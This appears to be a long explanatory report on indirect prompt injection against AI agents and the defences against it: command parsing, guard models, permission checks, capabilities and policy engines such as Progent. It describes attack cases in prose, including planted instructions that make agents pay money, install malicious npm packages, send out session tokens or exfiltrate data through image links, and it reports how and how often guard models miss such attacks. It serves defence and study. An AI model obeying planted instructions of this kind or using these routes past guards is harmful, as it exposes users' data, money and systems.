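In the same week, the security company Forcepoint published ten injections from live websites. Sewani's *10 Indirect Prompt Injection Payloads Caught in the Wild* presents them as evidence that attackers are already using the technique. Two were relatively mild. One told models not to answer questions about a page, and the other told them to credit a named consultant and recommend his services. Infosecurity Magazine's *Researchers Uncover 10 In-the-Wild Prompt Injection Payloads Targeting AI Agents* describes more dangerous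 ones, which asked coding agents to delete files, requested a secret API key, or gave complete instructions for a $5,000 PayPal payment. Sewani infers from the exact amount and steps that whoever wrote the payment text meant it for immediate use. Those details plausibly show intent, but there is no sign that any agent paid.

In July 2026, the security company Zscaler found websites with hidden text meant to make agents send cryptocurrency payments (Mascellino, 2026, *Indirect Prompt Injection in Web Content Targets AI Agents*). Attackers also plant instructions in the add-ons that agents use. Between July and October 2026, Ox Security examined 542,207 open-source components, including MCP servers, which supply agents with tools, and agent skills, which are packaged instructions for particular jobs. *Researchers Find a New AI Attack Path*, in Infosecurity Magazine, reports injected instructions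 or manipulated tool descriptions in 22 per cent of the servers and 26 per cent of the skills flagged as suspicious. Because these figures cover only flagged components, they do not show how common the problem is among all add-ons. They do suggest that an attacker's text often arrives with a tool that the user chose to install.

### Demonstrations and real victims

Most of the well-known cases are demonstrations. In *AI agent security*, Constantin (2026) counts four research teams that each broke agents in a different way within ten days in July 2026. Their targets included Claude for Chrome and an agent's memory. Such demonstrations prove that a product is vulnerable, but they don't measure how often criminals exploit it.

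EchoLeak (CVE-2025-32711), a flaw in Microsoft 365 Copilot that researchers at Aim Security found in 2025, belongs in the same group. The earlier input was an outsider's email containing hidden instructions, which could stay in the mailbox until the user asked a question that led Copilot to retrieve it. Copilot then placed private data in the address of an image in its reply, and the user's software sent the data out when it tried to load the image. The attack relied on the user's own permission to read the data. Microsoft fixed the flaw on its servers and said it knew of no affected customers. EchoLeak is a borderline case of command hijacking because Copilot only wrote a reply, and the software that displayed it made the request.

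Few public cases involve a real victim, but others may have gone unnoticed. A successful attack can leave no sign in the agent's answer, as thousands did in the Gray Swan competition, and in most logs the resulting command looks like the user's own.

In a 2026 case described in TechRadar's *AI agents tricked by a rogue downloads file into running dangerous malware*, the security firm Forever Security says it caught an attack on a customer's computer. The earlier input was a file called AGENTS.md in the Downloads folder, disguised as engineering notes. Coding agents treat a file of that name as instructions for the folder they are working in. This one contained instructions to install a malicious package from npm, a public library of JavaScript code, and to send out session tokens, the credentials that keep a user logged in. The agent would have done both with the user's own access to the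 machine.

The delay is unknown because nobody established when or how the file arrived. Forever Security suspects that a compromised website delivered it through the browser, which can save some kinds of file without asking. The firm says it stopped the attack before any meaningful damage, and it is unclear how much the customer's agent had done by then. Its researchers later reproduced the attack on Codex and Claude Code.

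No patch followed, since both agents were reading the file as their developers intended. Forever Security instead advises users not to start an agent in the Downloads folder, to read any instruction file they did not write, and to leave approval prompts and sandboxes switched on.

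## Checking a command before it runs

In the payroll story, the harness extracts a `send_email` call from the model's text and passes the arguments to the email tool, which sends the file. A shell command also goes through the shell, which rewrites it before starting any program. Software can inspect the command at each of these steps. OWASP's 2025 list of risks for language-model applications uses the term "improper output handling" for passing a model's output to other software without adequate validation.

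### Structure and values

The harness can check each call against a schema, a formal description of the arguments a tool accepts. The schema for `send_email` might require an email address for the recipient, a subject line and a list of attachments. A call fails if it names a tool that does not exist, omits the recipient or puts a sentence where a number belongs. The harness should reject such a call rather than repair it, because a repair would be partly guesswork.

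The payroll email passes this test, since its recipient is a well-formed address and its attachment is an ordinary file name.

A stricter check compares the values with limits set beforehand, such as a maximum payment, a set of account numbers or a list of web domains. Suppose the company allows the chatbot to send payroll files only to the payroll office and the contractor's real address. The attacker's address is not on the list, so the harness blocks the email. It also blocks the version attempted three weeks later, after the false address has passed through a summary and a shared memory, because the check does not depend on how the chatbot obtained the address.

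The harness must compare the whole address, since the attacker chose one that resembles an internal mailbox. The list of permitted recipients must also be stored where the agent cannot edit it. Even then, the agent can send the wrong file to a permitted recipient, and if a recipient's address changes, the harness will block legitimate emails until somebody updates the list. The address check also does not determine whether this employee may send payroll data at all.

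Many security rules cannot be written as a list of commands, file paths or domains. *When "Do Not" Is Not Deny* (2026) compares the rules that developers write for Claude Code in plain English with the product's built-in controls, which match only those three things. "Never commit secrets", for example, depends on what a file contains, which the controls do not check. A classifier estimated that the controls covered 16.6 per cent of the rules, but only about 35 per cent of the matches it found agreed with human judgements.

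### Why shell commands need parsing

Before running a command, a shell such as Bash replaces variables with their values, removes quotation marks, expands wildcards and runs any nested commands. Two strings that look nothing alike can therefore do the same thing, so a filter that searches the original string for forbidden words can miss a forbidden command that the shell will run.

Claude Code versions before 1.0.93 had a flaw of this kind, CVE-2025-66032. The program was meant to recognise commands that only read data, but a parsing error in the harness let an attacker disguise other commands as read-only with abbreviated options and a variable that the shell turns into spaces. *CARE* notes that reliable exploitation required untrusted content in the agent's context. Outside text could therefore lead to such commands running on the user's machine.

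A better check parses the command into programs, arguments, redirections and nested commands, then applies rules to those parts. This distinguishes a command that deletes files from one that searches a document for the words "delete files". *PARALLAX* (Fokou, 2026) describes a design that separates the agent from the software that executes its commands, and checks each shell command against rules after expanding variables and aliases. The checker and the shell still have to parse the command the same way, because any difference between them might let a harmful command pass the check.

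### When an approved program does something else

Once the harness has parsed a command, approving the program by name is not enough, because the arguments can change what the program does. MITRE's catalogue of software weaknesses lists this problem as CWE-88, argument injection, in which text meant as a value reaches another program as an extra argument or option. The attacker does not need to add a second command. For example, `find` normally searches for files, but some of its options delete the files it finds or start another program, so a harness that approves `find` by name also approves those uses.

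Some programs can run an attacker's code without any unusual options. *Four Ways to Deploy More Secure AI Agents*, a July 2026 post by NVIDIA's AI Red Team, gives two everyday examples: `pytest`, which runs a project's tests, and `npm install`, which installs JavaScript packages. Both can execute code they find in the project or package, so approving either command lets an attacker who controls that code run anything.

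Users often grant approvals this broad. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that by June 2026, 49.5 per cent of active command-line users had written a rule allowing some shell commands to run without a prompt. Five per cent allowed any shell command, and another 43 per cent allowed an interpreter such as Python, which is nearly as broad because a Python program can do almost anything a shell can. Claude Code ignores these broad rules when its automatic review is on, but keeps narrow ones, such as permission to run a code formatter.

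### Safer ways to run a command

A harness can often avoid the shell entirely. It can pass the operating system a fixed list of arguments and let the model supply only one value:

```
run(["grep", "-e", term, "notes.txt"])
```

This searches `notes.txt` for whatever the model supplies as `term`. No shell reads `term`, so a semicolon or dollar sign in it is not treated as shell syntax. Parameterised SQL queries work on the same principle.

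The list alone does not prevent argument injection, because `grep` might treat a search term that starts with a hyphen as an option. The `-e` marks the next item as the search term. Many other programs accept a double hyphen to mark the end of their options. If a program has no such marker, the harness can reject values that start with a hyphen.

A purpose-built tool gives the attacker even less to change. The company could replace general email access with `send_payroll_file(month)`, a tool whose code takes the recipient from the payroll department's settings. The chatbot then couldn't pass the tool a false address from its context. But someone has to write and maintain a tool for every job, which is practical for payroll but less so for an agent that repairs unfamiliar software. NVIDIA recommends avoiding command-line tools where possible and, where an agent needs one, using a strict list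 of permitted commands and an isolated environment.

The harness should also resolve each file path to its real location before deciding whether the agent may use it, because a path can lead out of a permitted folder through the parent folder or a symbolic link, which is a file that points to another location. It should let the agent write only to folders from which nothing executes. NVIDIA's testers point out that an agent without a shell can still cause code to run by writing to a start-up file that another program later executes.

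The file must also stay the same between the check and its use. If the harness approves a path and then opens the file, another process may redirect a symbolic link in between. Security engineers call this a time-of-check to time-of-use flaw. A tool can avoid it by opening the file once, then checking and using only that open file. Likewise, the harness should execute the exact call it approved, not a new version from the model.

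### How CARE checks shell commands

*CARE* examines one Bash command at a time. It receives the command, the agent's working folder, the location of the user's home folder and enough information about the file system to resolve symbolic links, but not the user's request or the conversation.

The guard first puts the command into a standard form without running it, which involves removing wrappers and undoing simple disguises. It then gives the command four scores between 0 and 1:

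- s_sem rates the program's purpose. Reading a file scores 0, transferring data over a network scores 0.40 and destroying data scores 1.
- s_path rates the files involved. Reading from a system folder scores 0.10 and writing to one scores 0.70, while any access to a private key scores at least 0.85.
- s_pat measures how closely the command matches 139 known dangerous patterns, with more weight for patterns from established public catalogues.
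- δ_struct rates the command's structure. Sending the output of one program straight to an interpreter scores 1.

The guard combines them as

score = 0.3 s_sem + 0.3 s_path + 0.3 s_pat + 0.1 δ_struct

The system allows commands that score below 0.15 and blocks those that score 0.35 or more. Between these limits, it blocks commands with strong evidence against them, such as access to a secret file, and sends the rest to a language model with an instruction to block when uncertain. It also blocks commands that it cannot parse if they contain a high-risk term.

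The main test used 549 commands, 220 of them dangerous. The guard caught 75.91 per cent of the dangerous commands and blocked three of the 329 safe ones, a false-alarm rate of 0.91 per cent. The 95 per cent confidence interval for that rate is 0.3 to 2.6 per cent. The average delay was 2.32 milliseconds, but most decisions took well under a millisecond because only 23 commands needed the language model.

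| Guard | Dangerous commands caught | Safe commands blocked | Average delay |
|---|---|---|---|
| String matching with 22 rules | 17.27% | 0% | 0.01 ms |
| Language model judging every command | 67.27% | 11.25% | 45.90 ms |
| Granite Guardian, a general safety model | 82.27% | 45.90% | 17.25 ms |
| *CARE* without its language model | 75.91% | 1.82% | 0.34 ms |
| *CARE* | 75.91% | 0.91% | 2.32 ms |

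Parsing explains at most part of the gap between string matching and *CARE*, because the string matcher also had far fewer rules. When the researchers removed the layer that analyses structure, detection fell only to 73.18 per cent. It fell to 42.27 per cent without the ratings of what each program does, and to 52.73 per cent without the path ratings. Knowing what a program does and which files it touches evidently mattered more than the structural score.

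The guard did less well on commands from other collections, where its false-alarm rate rose to between 8.13 and 13.04 per cent. On published exploit code, simple string matching had an F1 score of 81.52 per cent, compared with 66.33 per cent for the guard. F1 combines missed attacks and false alarms into one measure. Such code often repeats familiar destructive phrases, which string matching can detect.

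In another test, the researchers had a language model write 600 attack commands and ran them in a sandbox. Without a guard, 74.83 per cent ran successfully. The full guard reduced this to 52.50 per cent, but the version without a language model reduced it further, to 37.33 per cent. The guard's language model had approved attacks that the fixed rules would have blocked. *CARE* offers a plausible explanation: the same model wrote and judged the attacks.

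### A routine command that nobody requested

One command in *CARE* copies a folder of compiled software to another computer with `rsync`, a common file-transfer program. It scores 0.40 for transferring data over a network and 0.75 for matching a known pattern. The weighted total is 0.3 × 0.40 + 0.3 × 0.75 = 0.345, just below the limit for automatic blocking. The language model approves the command as routine.

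The guard was right to approve the command, which was a legitimate deployment. But the command would be identical if a planted instruction had chosen the destination. If an attacker had the agent copy an ordinary-looking folder of payroll files to a computer with a plausible name, the guard could well approve that too, because nothing in the command shows who asked for it.

*Same Operation, Different Permission* (2026) tests the same operation in four authorisation contexts. A guard that receives only the operation must give the same answer in all four, so it will be wrong in at least one whenever the correct answers differ.

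Fokou's design also has this limitation, because its model judge receives only the type of action and its content. The system blocked 98.9 per cent of 280 attacks with no false alarms, but Fokou built both the system and the test. The test sent harmful calls directly to the guard. This is a sound way to simulate a fully compromised agent, but it gives little evidence of whether the guard would stop an ordinary email to the wrong person.

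### Comparing a command with the user's task

A guard with access to the user's request can detect some of these unrequested commands. Usually, a second language model compares the request with the proposed call. An attacker may be able to manipulate this model too if its input includes the planted text, so designers limit what it receives.

| Guard | Information it receives | Information withheld |
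|---|---|---|
| *CARE* | The command and file-system details | The user's request, the conversation and tool results |
| Fokou's model judge | The type of action and its content | The task and the conversation |
| AgentVisor | The developer's instructions, the user's request, the proposed call and a summary of earlier steps | Raw tool results |
| Claude Code's auto mode | The user's messages and the agent's tool calls | The agent's own text and tool results |

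In *AgentVisor* (Ying, Wang and colleagues, 2026), the second model checks whether the tool suits the assistant's role, whether the action serves the user's request and whether the arguments match what the user specified. The last check covers cases where the user asks to email one person and an injection substitutes another. If a call fails a check, the agent receives an explanation and has one chance to propose a different call.

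The original payroll email should fail the second check, since a question about a payslip gives no reason to export everyone's pay records. The version three weeks later is harder to catch, because the clerk did ask the chatbot to send the file. If the summary of earlier steps includes the false address from memory, the call may seem to match her request.

Attacks reportedly succeeded 0.65 per cent of the time against agents using AgentVisor, with an average loss of 1.45 percentage points on ordinary tasks. On AgentDojo, six of the seven attacks succeeded less than 4 per cent of the time against an undefended GPT-4o agent, so the seventh is more informative. AgentVisor reduced that attack's success rate from 45.14 to 0.69 per cent, while the share of user tasks completed rose from 57.74 to 63.75 per cent. Ordinary tasks took about 1.4 times as long with AgentVisor.

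Much of this usefulness comes from allowing suspicious calls to be corrected. When Ying and colleagues blocked these calls without allowing a correction, the agent completed only 13.33 per cent of tasks under indirect attack, compared with 66.67 per cent with the correction. But the harness executes the corrected call without checking it again, which a determined attacker might exploit, although further rounds of checking did not reduce the attacks' success rate in their tests. Their adaptive attack used text instructing the guard to ignore its security check, a much weaker test than the automated searches that broke other published defences.

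Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, published in March 2026, describes a similar judge for coding agents. A quick first stage clears most actions and flags the rest for a second stage, which reasons about them. The judge treats choices the agent made by itself as unauthorised unless the user approved them. It also examines the contents of scripts the agent wrote, so the agent should not be able to hide a dangerous operation inside an innocent-looking command.

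The judge blocked 0.4 per cent of 10,000 real tool calls that it should have allowed. It missed 5.7 per cent of 1,000 synthetic attempts to send data out and 17 per cent of 52 real actions in which an agent had gone beyond its instructions. With only 52 cases, the true miss rate on such actions could be from about 9 to 30 per cent. In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the judge detected the danger but wrongly classified the action as one the user had consented to. For example, it could treat a request to "clean up" a code change as permission to overwrite the project's history.

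Withholding tool results also removes evidence the judge could use. If the user says "cancel my job" and the agent tries to cancel job abc123, the judge cannot check whether the agent found that ID in a real list or made it up. Anthropic accepts this loss of information in return for resistance to injection.

Later results vary widely:

- Apollo Research, an AI safety company, inserted synthetic attacks into real coding sessions. Anthropic reports that the judge's miss rate fell from 12 to 7 per cent after it had strengthened the judge in response.
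- In a test by Trajectory Labs, which Anthropic commissioned, none of 720 injection attempts succeeded against three Claude models with auto mode on. The attackers had tuned the injections to an older Claude model, and the newer models resisted almost all of them without the judge, so the result says little about the judge itself.
- The same test says more about OpenAI's Codex. Its automatic review reduced the success rate against GPT-5.6 Sol from 19.03 to 5.83 per cent.
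- besthub.dev's *Can Claude Code’s Auto Mode Replace Human Review?*, a second-hand account of another study, reports that auto mode missed 115 of 142 actions that exceeded the user's permission in deliberately ambiguous tasks. Some never reached the judge, but it still missed 70.3 per cent of those that did.

Some of He and colleagues' delegation attacks got past Claude Code's automatic review, even though Anthropic says the judge checks each task before the main agent hands it to a subagent.

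NVIDIA's Red Team is more pessimistic about model judges. It writes that three general techniques "reliably defeat these sorts of controls", which include safety instructions in prompts and second models acting as judges. One technique is to present a harmful action as legitimate, for instance by claiming to be an administrator debugging the agent. The team's post gives no success rates, and the testers could talk directly to most of the agents it covers.

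NVIDIA identifies a problem with package installation that withholding tool results does not solve. If a user asks an agent to set up a project and the agent proposes `npm install`, the command fits the request even if an attacker controls one of the packages. NVIDIA therefore recommends fixed controls outside the model as the first line of defence.

A judge can also fail to give a usable answer. In *Same Operation, Different Permission*, a guard called PolicyGuard returned an invalid label for 67 of 160 inputs. The harness needs a rule for these cases. *CARE* blocks the command when its judge's answer is unreadable, but two of the model judges it was compared with allowed the command.

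### Why most alarms will be false

Even an accurate guard produces mostly false alarms when hijacked commands are rare. Let p be the share of commands that are hijacked, d the share of those that the guard detects and f the share of legitimate commands that it wrongly flags. The chance that an alarm is genuine is

P(hijacked, given an alarm) = pd / (pd + (1 − p)f)

Suppose a company's agents run 2,000 commands a day and one in 10,000 is hijacked. That is an average of 0.2 hijacked commands a day, or one every five days. A guard that detects 95 per cent of hijacked commands and wrongly flags 1 per cent of legitimate ones would catch 0.19 hijacked commands a day and raise about 20 false alarms. Only about one in 106 of its alarms would be genuine.

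The same calculation with published figures gives similar results:

| Guard | Detection | False-alarm rate | False alarms a day | Genuine alarms |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Example | 95% | 1% | 20 | 0.9% |
| *CARE*, main test | 75.91% | 0.91% | 18 | 0.8% |
| Auto mode, synthetic data theft | 94.3% | 0.4% | 8 | 2.3% |

At the false-alarm rates that *CARE* had on the other collections, the company would get about 160 to 260 false alarms a day. The paper's example is more favourable because it assumes that one command in 100 is dangerous. Of every 10,000 commands in that example, the guard correctly blocks 76 and wrongly blocks about 90, so nearly half its alarms are genuine. In the company's case, where one command in 10,000 is hijacked, the false-alarm rate would have to fall to about one in 10,500 for half the alarms to be genuine.

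Sending every alarm to a person is unlikely to work well. According to Anthropic, Claude Code users approve 97 per cent of permission prompts. In an experiment with 1,053 paid testers, the researchers replaced one prompt with a clearly dangerous command. Only 13.6 per cent of the testers rejected it, while auto mode blocked 89 per cent of the same commands. Testers rejected about 17 per cent of the dangerous commands early in a session but 5 per cent after 50 or more prompts. They may have been less careful than usual because they had nothing of their own at risk in the test environment, but the decline suggests that frequent prompts make people less attentive.

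When auto mode refuses a command, it usually returns the refusal to the agent without involving the user. The agent then looks for a safer way to continue, so it usually needs just one more attempt after a false alarm. A hijacked agent can also try again, so Claude Code stops and asks the user after three refusals in a row or 20 in a session.

A list of approved recipients raises fewer alarms. It blocks the payroll email every time, and it raises false alarms only for legitimate recipients who are not yet on the list. A company may anyway want someone to confirm a new address before payroll data is sent to it.

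## Checking whether the agent has permission

A list of approved recipients limits where the payroll file can go, but not who can have it sent. The list allows the same transfers whether the request comes from an employee asking about her own payslip or from the clerk who runs the payroll. The result of a permission check also depends on who is asking and what they asked for.

### The confused deputy

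*The Confused Deputy* (Hardy, 1988) describes a fault at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. Tymshare's compiler, a program that turns source code into runnable software, kept usage statistics in a file in its own folder, so the engineers had given it permission to write any file there. The compiler could also save debugging output to a file that the customer named. One customer named Tymshare's billing file, which was in the same folder. Because the compiler had permission to write to that file, the operating system let it overwrite the billing records.

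Hardy argues that the compiler could not refuse every file in the folder, because some customers might have legitimate access to one, and that banning only the billing file's name would have left other sensitive files exposed. In his view, the problem was that the compiler had authority from both its own licence and the customer who ran it, but could not tell the operating system which authority it was using. Tymshare added a way to switch between the two, but some applications soon needed more than two sources of authority.

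His solution is a capability, a reference that both identifies a resource and grants the right to use it. The customer would give the compiler a capability for the output file instead of the file's name. A customer without access to the billing file would be unable to supply a capability for it.

The payroll chatbot is in the same position as the compiler. It holds credentials for everyone's pay records but works for an employee who has no right to see other people's. It also reads text from the person who edited the wiki page, who has no authority, and its model processes that text in the same context as the employee's request. If the company gave the chatbot only a capability for the employee's own payslip in each conversation, the hidden text could not make it export anyone else's records.

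Capabilities help less when the chatbot works for the payroll clerk. She can properly give it access to both the payroll file and email, but the model still determines how the chatbot combines them. Rajani, Garg and Rezk relate protection from confused deputy attacks to information-flow integrity, which concerns whether untrusted data can influence trusted operations, in *On access control, capabilities, their equivalence, and confused deputy attacks*.

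### The user, the agent and the task

A permission check can combine three limits. Let U be the set of commands that the user may have carried out, A the set that the agent may carry out, and T the set that the present task needs. A command c may run only if

c ∈ U ∩ A ∩ T

Each member of these sets is a complete call, including its arguments, so T can contain an email to the payroll contractor without containing the same email to anyone else. The underlying principle is that a program should have only the access its work requires, which security engineers call least privilege.

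| Request | Proposed command | In U? | In A? | In T? |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| An employee asks how to check her payslip | Email everyone's payroll file | No | Yes | No |
| A clerk asks for a summary of a wiki page | Email the payroll file to the contractor | Yes | Yes | No |
| A clerk asks for a change to a colleague's salary | Change the salary record | Yes | No | Yes |
| A clerk asks the chatbot to send the file to the contractor | Email it to the contractor's address on file | Yes | Yes | Yes |

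Only the last command should run.

Companies often leave out one of the limits. NVIDIA's testers found several agents that held individual users' credentials but answered any authorised user of the internal network. Those agents did not enforce U, so one employee could use another's access. NVIDIA recommends restricting who can use each agent and matching its permissions to those of the person using it.

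OpenAI's *Agent security in the enterprise* (2026) describes an invoice agent that notices a subscription to a document-signing service is about to lapse and tries to renew it so that invoice processing can continue. The supplier and the amount may both be within the agent's limits, but nobody authorised it to sign contracts. No attacker is involved here, but checking whether the agent has that authority would also stop a planted instruction to renew the subscription.

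U also has to accompany a request from one agent to another. Li, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *Security Considerations for Artificial Intelligence Agents*, warn that an agent with few privileges can get a more privileged agent to do things the first agent could not do itself. If the chatbot passes the employee's request to an email subagent, the subagent must check the employee's permissions, not the chatbot's.

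### Where and when to check

A company could write "never send payroll data outside the company" in the chatbot's standing instructions. The model's output would then depend on both that sentence and whatever the wiki page contains. A check in ordinary code, outside the model, applies the same rule however persuasive the planted text is.

The location of that code determines which commands it can stop, and *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents* (2026), a survey, makes the same point about all such systems. A check on the email tool, for instance, can't stop the agent from sending email through a shell that can reach the mail server. OpenAI therefore advises companies to enforce authorisation separately at each system a command affects, here the mail server and the payroll database.

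A permission check can go out of date because permissions and circumstances change. The Australian Signals Directorate's *Careful adoption of agentic AI services* (2026), written jointly with five other cyber security agencies, warns against checking an agent's permissions only when the system starts. In its invented example, a company connects a scheduling component to a customer-support agent and grants it broad access at start-up. An attacker later compromises the component, but the agent still relies on the permission decisions stored at start-up. The attacker can therefore use account-management functions that should have required a check for each request.

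An approval from a person can go stale in the same way. Suppose the clerk approves an email that sends the March payroll file to the contractor, and the harness records this as "`send_email` allowed for this session". An hour later, the chatbot reads a poisoned page and proposes emailing the staff's home addresses to a stranger. The stored approval covers this call too, because the harness recorded only the tool's name, not the file and recipient the clerk had approved.

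A safer harness would store the approval with the exact arguments, the user and the task, and cancel it after one use. Several systems from 2026 work towards this:

- *TraceGrant* (2026) ties each proposed action to an unfinished part of the task, evidence for its sensitive arguments and a remaining budget. Permission to make one payment runs out when the agent makes it.
- *AgentCap* (2026) uses capabilities much as Hardy proposed. A policy engine issues a token for a proposed call, the agent presents the token with the call, and a gateway verifies it before passing the call to the tool. The engine also checks the session for missing prerequisites and forbidden combinations of actions.
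- *PolicyGuide* (2026) blocks every tool that changes data until the conditions for that particular tool are met. However, a language model judges whether they are, so the block is only as reliable as that judgement.

### How Progent writes and applies a policy

Shi, He and colleagues (2025), in *Progent*, put a policy check between an agent and its tools. A policy is a list of rules, and each rule has this form:

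```
allow | forbid   tool   when { conditions },   fallback action
```

The conditions in Progent's rules can compare a call's arguments with fixed values, look them up in a list or match them against a pattern. Progent applies the "forbid" rules before the "allow" rules and blocks any call that matches neither. The fallback for a blocked call can stop the agent, consult the user or return an error message. By default, it sends the agent a message giving the reason, and the agent can continue with the user's task.

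Two rules for the payroll example might look like this:

```
forbid send_email
  when { attachments[0] match "payroll_.*"
         and not (to in ["payroll@example.com",
                         "files@contractor.example"]) },
  fallback return "Payroll files may go only to addresses on file."
```

allow send_email
  when { to = "files@contractor.example"
         and attachments.length = 1
         and attachments[0] = "payroll_last_month.csv" }
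```

The company would put the first rule in a generic policy, which applies to every task and overrides anything more specific. The second rule is specific to the clerk's task. Neither rule allows the attacker's address, `hr-reports@example.com`.

The first rule also mistakenly inspects only the first attachment, so an email with the payroll file attached second would get past it. The second rule limits the damage because it accepts only a single attachment to a single address, and Progent blocks everything else. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) criticises Progent on this ground, arguing that handwritten policies remain prone to error despite its validation tools.

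Progent's rules refer to tools and arguments but not to the user's identity, and Shi and colleagues assume the user is honest. So the company would have to load the second rule only for payroll clerks, or rely on the payroll system to refuse everyone else.

Nobody could write a rule by hand for every request, so a language model writes a policy for each task before the agent has read any outside content, using only the user's request and the list of tools. After each tool call, a model decides, without seeing the result, whether the policy may need to change. If so, it reads the result and proposes a new policy.

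Because the result could contain an attack, ordinary software compares the two policies. Let A(P) be the set of calls that policy P allows. A new policy P′ is a narrowing if

A(P′) ⊆ A(P)

and otherwise it is an expansion. Progent uses an SMT solver, a program that determines whether a set of logical conditions can be satisfied, to look for any call that P′ allows and P does not. It applies a narrowing automatically, while an expansion needs approval. Replacing one permitted recipient with another counts as an expansion, even though the number of recipients stays the same. Between approvals, the set of allowed calls can therefore only shrink or stay the same. Shi and colleagues call this monotonic confinement.

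In the paper's example, a user asks an agent to carry out the jobs listed in an email from Alice. The first policy allows only a search for that email. In the email, Alice asks for a summary of the user's recent mail to be posted to his own Slack account. This requires three more tools, so the policy must be expanded with approval. Once the agent has looked up the user's Slack name, the model narrows the policy to allow messages only to that name. One of the recent emails contains an instruction to forward the inbox to a stranger. Even if this leads the model to propose `send_email`, the solver reports an expansion and the approver can refuse it.

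The solver can only detect that the policy would allow something new. The approver still has to distinguish Alice's list from the stranger's instruction, because both requests for more access came by email.

Shi and colleagues regard narrowing as safe because it only removes permissions, but it can also lock in an attacker's choice. Suppose the clerk asks the chatbot to send the file to the contractor without giving an address, and the first policy allows any recipient. The chatbot looks up the contractor and finds the planted address. The model then restricts `send_email` to that address, which makes the attacker the only permitted recipient. The solver accepts the change because the new policy allows fewer calls. The task's own policy would then allow an email that the company's generic rule would still block.

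### Progent's results

Shi and colleagues tested Progent on AgentDojo and on Agent Security Bench (ASB), which covers ten kinds of agent. GPT-4o ran the agents and wrote the policies.

| Test | Setting | Attack success rate |
|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo | No defence | 39.9% |
| AgentDojo | First policy only, no updates | 2.5% |
| AgentDojo | Updates, with every expansion approved | 1.0% |
| AgentDojo | Updates, with careful human review | 0% |
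| ASB | No defence | 70.3% |
| ASB | Updates, with every expansion approved | 3.9% |
| ASB | Rules written by hand | 0% |

On AgentDojo, the attack success rate fell by 38.9 percentage points, and the first policy alone accounts for 37.4 of them. Most of the protection evidently came from setting the agent's permissions before it read anything an attacker might have written.

The results provide less evidence about monotonic confinement. Shi and colleagues approved every expansion to simulate a careless user, so the solver's warnings stopped nothing in those runs. The 1.0 per cent therefore mainly reflects how rarely the attacks fooled the model that wrote the policies. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* objects that this part of Progent relies on prompt engineering, and recommends having a separate model evaluate each update in isolation.

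On both tests, agents completed roughly as many ordinary tasks with Progent as without it. With a simpler defence, which used a model to remove irrelevant tools before the task began, agents completed fewer ordinary tasks and more attacks succeeded. This defence could not set conditions on a tool's arguments, so each tool was either fully available or unavailable.

Progent also helped models that already resisted most attacks, reducing the attack success rate against Claude Sonnet 4 from 6.8 to 0.5 per cent. Three adaptive attacks, including an automated search called AgentVigil, raised the success rate only slightly. Testing adaptive attacks gives stronger evidence than testing fixed attacks alone, but more powerful automated attackers have appeared since, such as the swarm that Kurakin and colleagues built.

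Most of the remaining failures on ASB involved malicious tools whose names and descriptions closely resembled those of legitimate ones. Shi and colleagues doubt that a person could have spotted them without knowing in advance which tools to trust. Progent can run as a proxy between an existing agent and its external tools, but then it cannot control the agent's built-in tools, because calls to them don't pass through the proxy.

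### Short-lived credentials and separate tools

A policy check in the harness protects little if the agent also holds a password that works anywhere. To avoid this, OpenAI's guide describes a system that creates a task token when someone gives the agent a task. The token records who asked and what the task covers. The harness exchanges it for a short-lived credential that works for one resource and one kind of action. A credential manager can keep the credential out of the model's context. In the payroll case, the harness would receive a credential for the employee's own payslip when she asked her question, and the payroll system would reject any attempt to use it for the whole company's file.

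Keeping credentials away from the model matters because it can disclose whatever it can read. NVIDIA's testers found passwords and tokens in environment variables, shell histories and configuration files that the agents could open. Even when the testers could not connect directly to the machine, they could often get the agent to reveal credentials in the chat.

Giving a credential a short lifetime mainly limits later misuse if it is stolen. The payroll email takes a few seconds and uses a credential that is still valid, so a ten-minute expiry time would not stop it.

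A company can also limit access by separating tools that read from tools that write. The six-agency guidance recommends distinct roles with clear boundaries, including a "Reader" and an "Actuator". The reader could search the wiki but not send anything, and the actuator could send email without opening wiki pages. But the two have to communicate, so if the reader reports an attacker's address as the contractor's new one, the actuator receives it from an agent it has reason to trust, as happened in Triedman and colleagues' attacks.

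Read-only access can also do harm. A chatbot that can only read data might show one employee another's salary, and OpenAI points out that a company cannot always undo a disclosure.

### The Rule of Two

Most permission rules judge one command at a time. Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025), published on 31 October 2025, instead limits what an agent can combine in one session. Unless a person or another reliable check supervises it, the agent may have at most two of these properties:

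- [A] It can process untrustworthy inputs.
- [B] It can access sensitive systems or private data.
- [C] It can change state or communicate externally.

Meta's rule builds on the programmer Simon Willison's "lethal trifecta" of private data, untrusted content and external communication. The rule's third property is broader than Willison's and also covers actions such as deleting a record.

The payroll chatbot has all three. The company could remove A by letting the chatbot read only pages from trusted staff, B by taking away its access to the payroll files, or C by limiting email to trusted recipients. Each change would stop the attack without requiring the model to recognise the planted text. An agent may also change configuration during a session. For example, it could browse the internet first, then permanently lose the ability to communicate before it opens internal systems.

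Critics object that useful agents tend to need all three properties. McKerchar writes in *Inside the lethal trifecta* that companies' agents already often combine private data, untrusted content and external communication. Evoke Security (2025), which sells security for AI agents, argues that restricting inputs makes an agent less useful, while asking a person to approve its actions "shifts the burden to the user". Meta concedes that some popular uses don't fit the rule well, such as background processes with no one available to approve actions.

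It is also doubtful that every pair of properties is safe. According to Conffab's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025), Meta's diagram labels every pair "Safe". Meta is more cautious in its text, which says that the rule aims to prevent the most serious consequences of prompt injection, and that excessive privileges and the agent's own mistakes remain separate problems.

Because the rule applies to a single session, it can miss untrusted content that the agent saved to memory in an earlier one. Three weeks after the wiki page was altered, the clerk asks the chatbot to send the payroll file. The chatbot can do this without opening an untrusted page, so it appears to have only B and C, but the false address is already in its memory. The rule protects this session only if the company treats notes derived from untrusted content as untrusted input. For an agent with a long-term memory, that could mean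 A is almost always present.

### The six-agency guidance of May 2026

*Careful adoption of agentic AI services* advises organisations to use agents only for low-risk and non-sensitive tasks, and never to grant them broad or unrestricted access. Read strictly, this rules out the payroll chatbot. CISA wrote the guidance with the US National Security Agency and the national cyber security centres of Australia, Canada, New Zealand and the UK, and announced it on 1 May (CISA, 2026).

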